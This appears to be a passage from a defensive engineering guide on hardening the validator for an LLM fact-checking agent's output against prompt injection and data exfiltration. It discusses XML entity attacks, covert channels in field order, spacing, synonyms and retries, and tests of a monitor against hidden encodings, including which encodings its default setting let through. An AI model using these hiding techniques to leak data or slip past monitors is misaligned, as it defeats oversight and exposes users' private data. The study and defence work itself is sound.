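The validator should also accept only one format. HashiCorp Vault, a program that stores passwords and keys, once used a lenient XML parser to read identity checks from Amazon's servers. Google's Project Zero team found that an attacker could bypass authentication completely by making the server reply in JSON and controlling part of the reply. The parser skipped everything that didn't look like XML and accepted a false identity from the rest. Python's `json.loads` rejects any text before or after the record, except whitespace.

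### XML entities

XML has a further hazard that JSON lacks. An XML document can define an entity, a short name that the parser replaces with a longer piece of text. The definition of an external entity gives an address instead of the text, and a parser that resolves the entity requests that address.

A hijacked model could put a stolen phone number in such an address. The number would leak during parsing, before the validator checked any field, even though the record has no field for links. External entities must therefore be switched off in the XML parser. This record doesn't need a document type declaration, the part of an XML file that defines entities, so the safest setting is to refuse them all.

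Entities that stay inside the document can also do damage. If each entity repeats the previous one ten times, nine levels expand into a billion copies, yet the definitions fit within 1,000 characters and pass the size limit. *CVE-2024-1455*, an entry in the US National Vulnerability Database (NVD), describes this flaw in LangChain, a popular library for building programs on language models. LangChain's parser for XML output expanded nested entities, so an attacker who manipulated the model could interrupt the service by making it run out of memory, but couldn't use the flaw to leak data. LangChain fixed it in version 0.1.35 by switching to defusedxml, a safer parser, according to Miggo's *CVE-2024-1455* (2024).

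A developer who can choose the format should choose JSON. If the model has to write XML, the validator should also reject repeated tags, attributes and comments, then copy the six values into the structure the JSON version uses so that all the later checks can stay the same.

### Checking the source, the quotation and the title

The range check accepts any source number from 0 to 9, so it accepts 7 even though page 7 never loaded. Looking the number up in the fetch log catches this.

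The validator adds the quotation's starting position to its length and checks that the passage ends within the stored text. A schema can't express this rule, because it depends on the length of a particular stored page. The validator also checks that a confidence of 0 appears only with `unclear`, although JSON Schema can express that rule because it involves only fixed values.

The validator then cuts out the passage and passes on the text. If it passed on only the position, another program might cut in the wrong place, because programming languages count characters differently. Python counts an emoji as one character and JavaScript usually counts it as two, so every position after an emoji would shift. The validator also uses the stored copy of the page, because the page's owner could change the live version after the model reads it and before the validator checks it.

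The title needs a check because the page's owner wrote it. An attacker could give a page on `attacker.example` the title "library.example: opening hours". When trusted code saves a page, it can compare any domain name in the title with the page's real host, and store the host in place of the title if they differ. This check can't catch a title such as "Town Library official site", which contains no domain name, so the display should also show the host beside every title.

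### Rewriting the record in a standard form

The same six values can be written as JSON in many ways, and a hijacked model can hide data in its choice. The six fields have 6! = 720 possible orders, so their order alone can carry log₂ 720 ≈ 9.5 bits, more than the verdict, confidence and source number carry together.

Spacing can carry far more data, because JSON allows four kinds of blank character between its parts and each blank can therefore encode 2 bits. A record with an empty summary takes at most 105 characters, which leaves room for 895 blanks under the size limit, or 1,790 bits. The model can also hide data by writing each letter of the summary either plainly or as a numeric code.

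The last step of the validator removes these choices by writing a new record from the parsed values:

```json
{"confidence":8,"quote_length":33,"quote_start":1240,"source":3,"summary":"The library's own page lists Sunday as a closing day.","verdict":"contradicted"}
```

This follows the rules in *JSON Canonicalization Scheme (JCS)*, by Rundgren, Jordan and Erdtman, which defines a fixed form of JSON for digital signatures because they fail if a single character changes. The form has no spacing between parts, sorts fields by name and allows only one way to write each number and string. It also rounds very precise numbers, but the whole numbers in this record are too small to be affected.

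Later programs should receive only the rewritten record, because they could misread the original. A developer who keeps the original for debugging should store it where neither an attacker nor another model can read it.

The standard form doesn't change what a string contains, so the summary can still carry its full 1,314 bits. The program that displays the report must therefore show the summary, quotation and title as plain text, with automatic links and previews switched off. The program creates the report's only link, using the address in the fetch log.

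### One valid record and three faulty ones

The library record passes every check. The user sees the verdict, the confidence, the summary, the quoted sentence, and a link to page 3 with its title and host. Each of the three faulty records below changes one thing in this record. Page 3 has 6,200 characters of stored text.

| Record | Change | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Valid | None | Accepted |
| Duplicate field | `source` appears as 3 and again as 7 | Rejected during parsing |
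| Missing page | `source` is 7 | Rejected because page 7 is not in the log |
| Impossible quotation | `quote_start` is 6190 | Rejected because the passage would end at character 6,223 |

An ordinary schema check would accept all three faulty records. The duplicate disappears before the schema applies, and the other two records have values within the permitted ranges.

The validator would also accept the original record with its verdict changed to `supported`. The quoted sentence would still be real, and a user who read it would see that it contradicts the verdict. A privileged model that receives only the verdict and the numbers could not detect the contradiction.

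Code can check Li's restaurant orders against a menu, but no such reference exists for an arbitrary claim about the world. A developer who wants the agent to act on the verdict could require agreement between sources on different domains, or ask a person to approve the action.

### How much the record can carry

The verdict, confidence and source number allow 4 × 11 × 10 = 440 combinations, so together they carry

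log₂ 440 ≈ 8.8 bits.

A quotation can start at any of 20,000 characters and have any of 300 lengths, which gives 6,000,000 positions, or

log₂ 6,000,000 ≈ 22.5 bits.

These figures are slightly too high. The rule about a confidence of 0 excludes 30 of the 440 combinations, and a passage that starts near the end of a page has fewer than 300 possible lengths. Together the two corrections come to about a tenth of a bit.

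The summary adds about 1,314 bits. The last column below gives the number of records that an attacker would need to steal a 16-digit card number, which takes 53 bits:

| Fields that the attacker can see | Capacity | Records needed |
|---|---|---|
| Verdict, confidence, source number | 8.8 bits | 7 |
| The same fields and the quotation position | 31.3 bits | 2 |
| All six fields | 1,345 bits | 1 |

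The developer can reduce the 22.5 bits by numbering the sentences on each page and having the model cite one of them. With at most 200 sentences per page, a citation carries log₂ 200 ≈ 7.6 bits, and the record without its summary carries 16.4. Numbering should also prevent many honest mistakes, because models process tokens rather than single characters and could easily be wrong about where character 1,240 falls.

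If the model receives only the claim and ten public pages, the claim is the only thing it can leak. Judging the claim doesn't require the user's other data, so withholding that data doesn't make the model worse at the task.

### Removing or isolating the summary

Removing the summary cuts the capacity from 1,345 bits to 31.3. If the developer then sends a privileged model only the numbers and the verdict, without the quotation or the title, no free text can carry injected instructions to that model.

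The user loses the explanation, which matters little when one sentence settles the question, as it does for the library. The loss matters more for a `disputed` verdict, because that verdict depends on at least two pages and the record quotes only one. The developer can fix this by adding a second source number and quotation position. These additions carry another 25.8 bits, bringing the total to 57.1, still less than a twentieth of what the full record carries.

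A fixed list of reasons, such as "the page is out of date" or "the pages refer to different years", can also replace the summary. A list of 16 reasons adds 4 bits. It works well when the same few explanations recur, but it can't describe an unusual case.

The developer can also keep the summary but have trusted code show it only on the user's screen. The code leaves it out of emails, shared reports and any log that another model reads. The user gets the full explanation, and other programs still receive at most 31.3 bits. However, the developer has to enforce this separation in every feature that uses the record, and a hijacked model can still lie to the user. This seems the best choice when only the tool's own user reads its answers. If the record goes to a public page or to an agent that can act, the developer should remove the summary.

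Rewording the summary is a weaker alternative. A hijacked model can hide a secret in innocent text by choosing between synonyms such as "closed" and "shut", at one bit per choice. The monitor paper tests a program that replaces such choices with a standard wording. The tests covered four kinds of choice, including contractions and active or passive sentences, with 40 trials each. The receiver recovered almost everything without the program, but with it got only 51.6% of the bits right, about as many as by guessing.

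But rewording has to preserve the meaning of the text, so if the model openly writes a client's name in the summary, the name will still be there afterwards.

### Retries and error messages

The figures above are for a single record. Metere gives a formula for repeated choices by an agent that may take D kinds of action. Each tool call has D + 1 possible outcomes, because the software can also refuse it, so K calls carry at most

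K × log₂(D + 1) bits.

With 10 kinds of action and 8 calls, there are 11⁸ ≈ 214 million possible sequences, or about 27.7 bits.

This upper limit counts only the kind of action the model takes, not the details of that action. Metere presents it as a limit on how much a hijacked model can leak per call. That claim is too strong, because one permitted web request can carry thousands of bits if the model writes the URL. The formula also omits messages to the user and the timing of calls.

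The formula suits the record better because the 440 combinations already cover every possible verdict, confidence and source number. If an agent checks 50 claims a day and an attacker can see all three fields each time, up to 439 bits a day can leak, enough for eight card numbers.

Retries add to this if the attacker can see what went wrong. Suppose the model gets three attempts, and a public status page shows which of five checks rejected each failed attempt: size, parsing, values, fetch log or quotation. The model can then send a message by failing in a chosen way:

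| Outcome | Number of possibilities |
|---|---|
| Accepted on the first attempt | 440 |
| Accepted on the second | 5 × 440 = 2,200 |
| Accepted on the third | 25 × 440 = 11,000 |
| Rejected three times | 125 |

The total is 13,765 possibilities, or 13.7 bits instead of 8.8, so the attacker needs four records instead of seven to leak a card number. If the status page showed only the final result, with the same message for every kind of rejection, three attempts would leak no more information than one. The detailed reason can go in a private log for the developer.

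*Bits Leaked per Query* describes the same relationship in attacks on the models themselves. *Bits Leaked per Query* (2025) derives the smallest number of queries that an attacker needs:

N = log(1/ε) / I,

where ε is the error rate that the attacker will accept and I is the information that each reply leaks. Doubling the leak per reply therefore halves the number of queries. Experiments on seven models closely followed this rule for three kinds of attack, including jailbreaks (prompts that get around a model's safety training) and theft of the system prompt.

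In those experiments, showing the model's reasoning or its token probabilities leaked about half a bit more per query and cut the typical number of queries for a jailbreak from thousands to tens. Under the formula, such a large drop means ordinary replies had been leaking only a small fraction of a bit each. These numbers don't transfer to a validator, but they suggest that a small extra signal, such as a detailed error message, helps an attacker most when the output is otherwise very restricted.

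### Tests of an outgoing-traffic monitor

The monitor, also by Metere, checks outgoing messages instead of restricting what the model may write. Metere built programs that hide random bits in ordinary-looking messages, sent the messages through the monitor, and measured how much a matching decoder could recover. Each text test had 20 trials. In the default setting, the monitor makes changes that a reader would not notice and blocks messages that clearly contain passwords or other credentials. Its other checks only record what they find. In the full setting, every check can change or block a message.

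| Where the data was hidden | Leak prevented, default | Leak prevented, full |
|---|---|---|
| Order of JSON fields | 100% | 100% |
| Invisible characters | 100% | 100% |
| Look-alike letters from other alphabets | 100% | 100% |
| Number of spaces | 0% | 100% |
| Repeated punctuation | 0% | 100% |
| Choice of synonyms | 0% | 100% |
| Base64 text | 0% | 100% |

The monitor detected all of these in every trial, but in the default setting it let four of them through unchanged. Metere reports an average reduction of 60.2% across eleven channels in that setting, but the results list default figures for only nine, which average 55.6%.

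The 100% figures apply only to the encodings that Metere tried, so others might still get past the monitor. Metere was also testing his own company's software. The result for field order is still convincing, because sorting the fields leaves the model no order to choose.

Timing was harder to control. Rounding the sending times left about a fifth of the timing channel open, and closing it required sending messages on a fixed schedule, which makes users wait. No setting removes the last bit, because a hijacked agent can always choose whether to send a message at all.

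The library record needs little of this machinery once the summary is gone. Its values come from short lists and ranges, and rewriting it removes the choice of order and spacing. It also makes a leak allowance easier to run, because each record uses a known number of bits. The monitor, by contrast, has to estimate how much hidden data a message might hold, and it deliberately estimates high, so a harmless attachment can use up the allowance. An allowance of 100 bits per recipient per day permits eleven library records with the verdict, confidence and source number, or three that also give a quotation position, but a single summary would exceed it.

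### When the validator rejects an honest record

Strict checks also reject legitimate records. The summary above can't contain "café" or a curly apostrophe, because the check allows only the 95 printable ASCII characters. Converting curly punctuation to straight before the check fixes most such cases in English. For other languages, the developer has to permit more characters and accept that the summary could carry more leaked data.

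Addresses cause more trouble, because one page can have many. The library record avoids the problem by citing pages by number. In a version where the model writes the address, an exact comparison would reject all three addresses below, although they lead to the page that the log lists as `https://www.library.example/opening-hours`:

| Address that the model writes | Difference | Repair |
|---|---|---|
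| `http://library.example/hours` | Redirects to the logged page | Log every address along the redirect |
| `https://www.library.example/opening-hours?utm_source=search` | Has a tracking parameter | Ignore a short list of known tracking parameters |
| `https://WWW.library.example/opening%2Dhours` | Has a capitalized host and an encoded hyphen | Convert both addresses to one spelling first |

These repairs are safe only if the program uses the log's copy of the address and throws away the model's. Otherwise an attacker could put the stolen phone number in `utm_source`. The validator would ignore that parameter and find a match, and opening the model's version would send the number.

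The repairs must also be narrow. If the validator ignored every parameter, it would treat `?page=1` and `?page=2` as the same page and might show a quotation from the wrong one. It can ignore capitalization in the host but not in the path, where it can matter. An encoded hyphen is equivalent to an ordinary one under RFC 3986, but an encoded slash can lead to a different page. The validator should decode each address only once, because decoding it again can turn it into another address.

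The validator must also parse the JSON before comparing addresses. JSON allows a backslash before each slash, so the same address can look different in the raw text. Bray warns that programs that compare strings before converting these escapes may wrongly find the strings unequal.

When a request is redirected, the log should record the address that finally supplied the text. The title, quotation and host shown to the user must all belong to that address. If the program displayed the first address instead, a redirect from a trusted site could make an attacker's page look like part of that site.

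Metere suggests running the stricter checks in a recording mode first, so a company can see what they would block. If the validator protects private data, that data can still leak during the trial. A developer can get the same information safely by running the validator on saved outputs before launch. Li recommends saving each output with the validator's decision, so developers can repeat the test whenever they change a rule. Some saved outputs may contain stolen data or injected instructions, so the test archive needs the same access restrictions as the original records.
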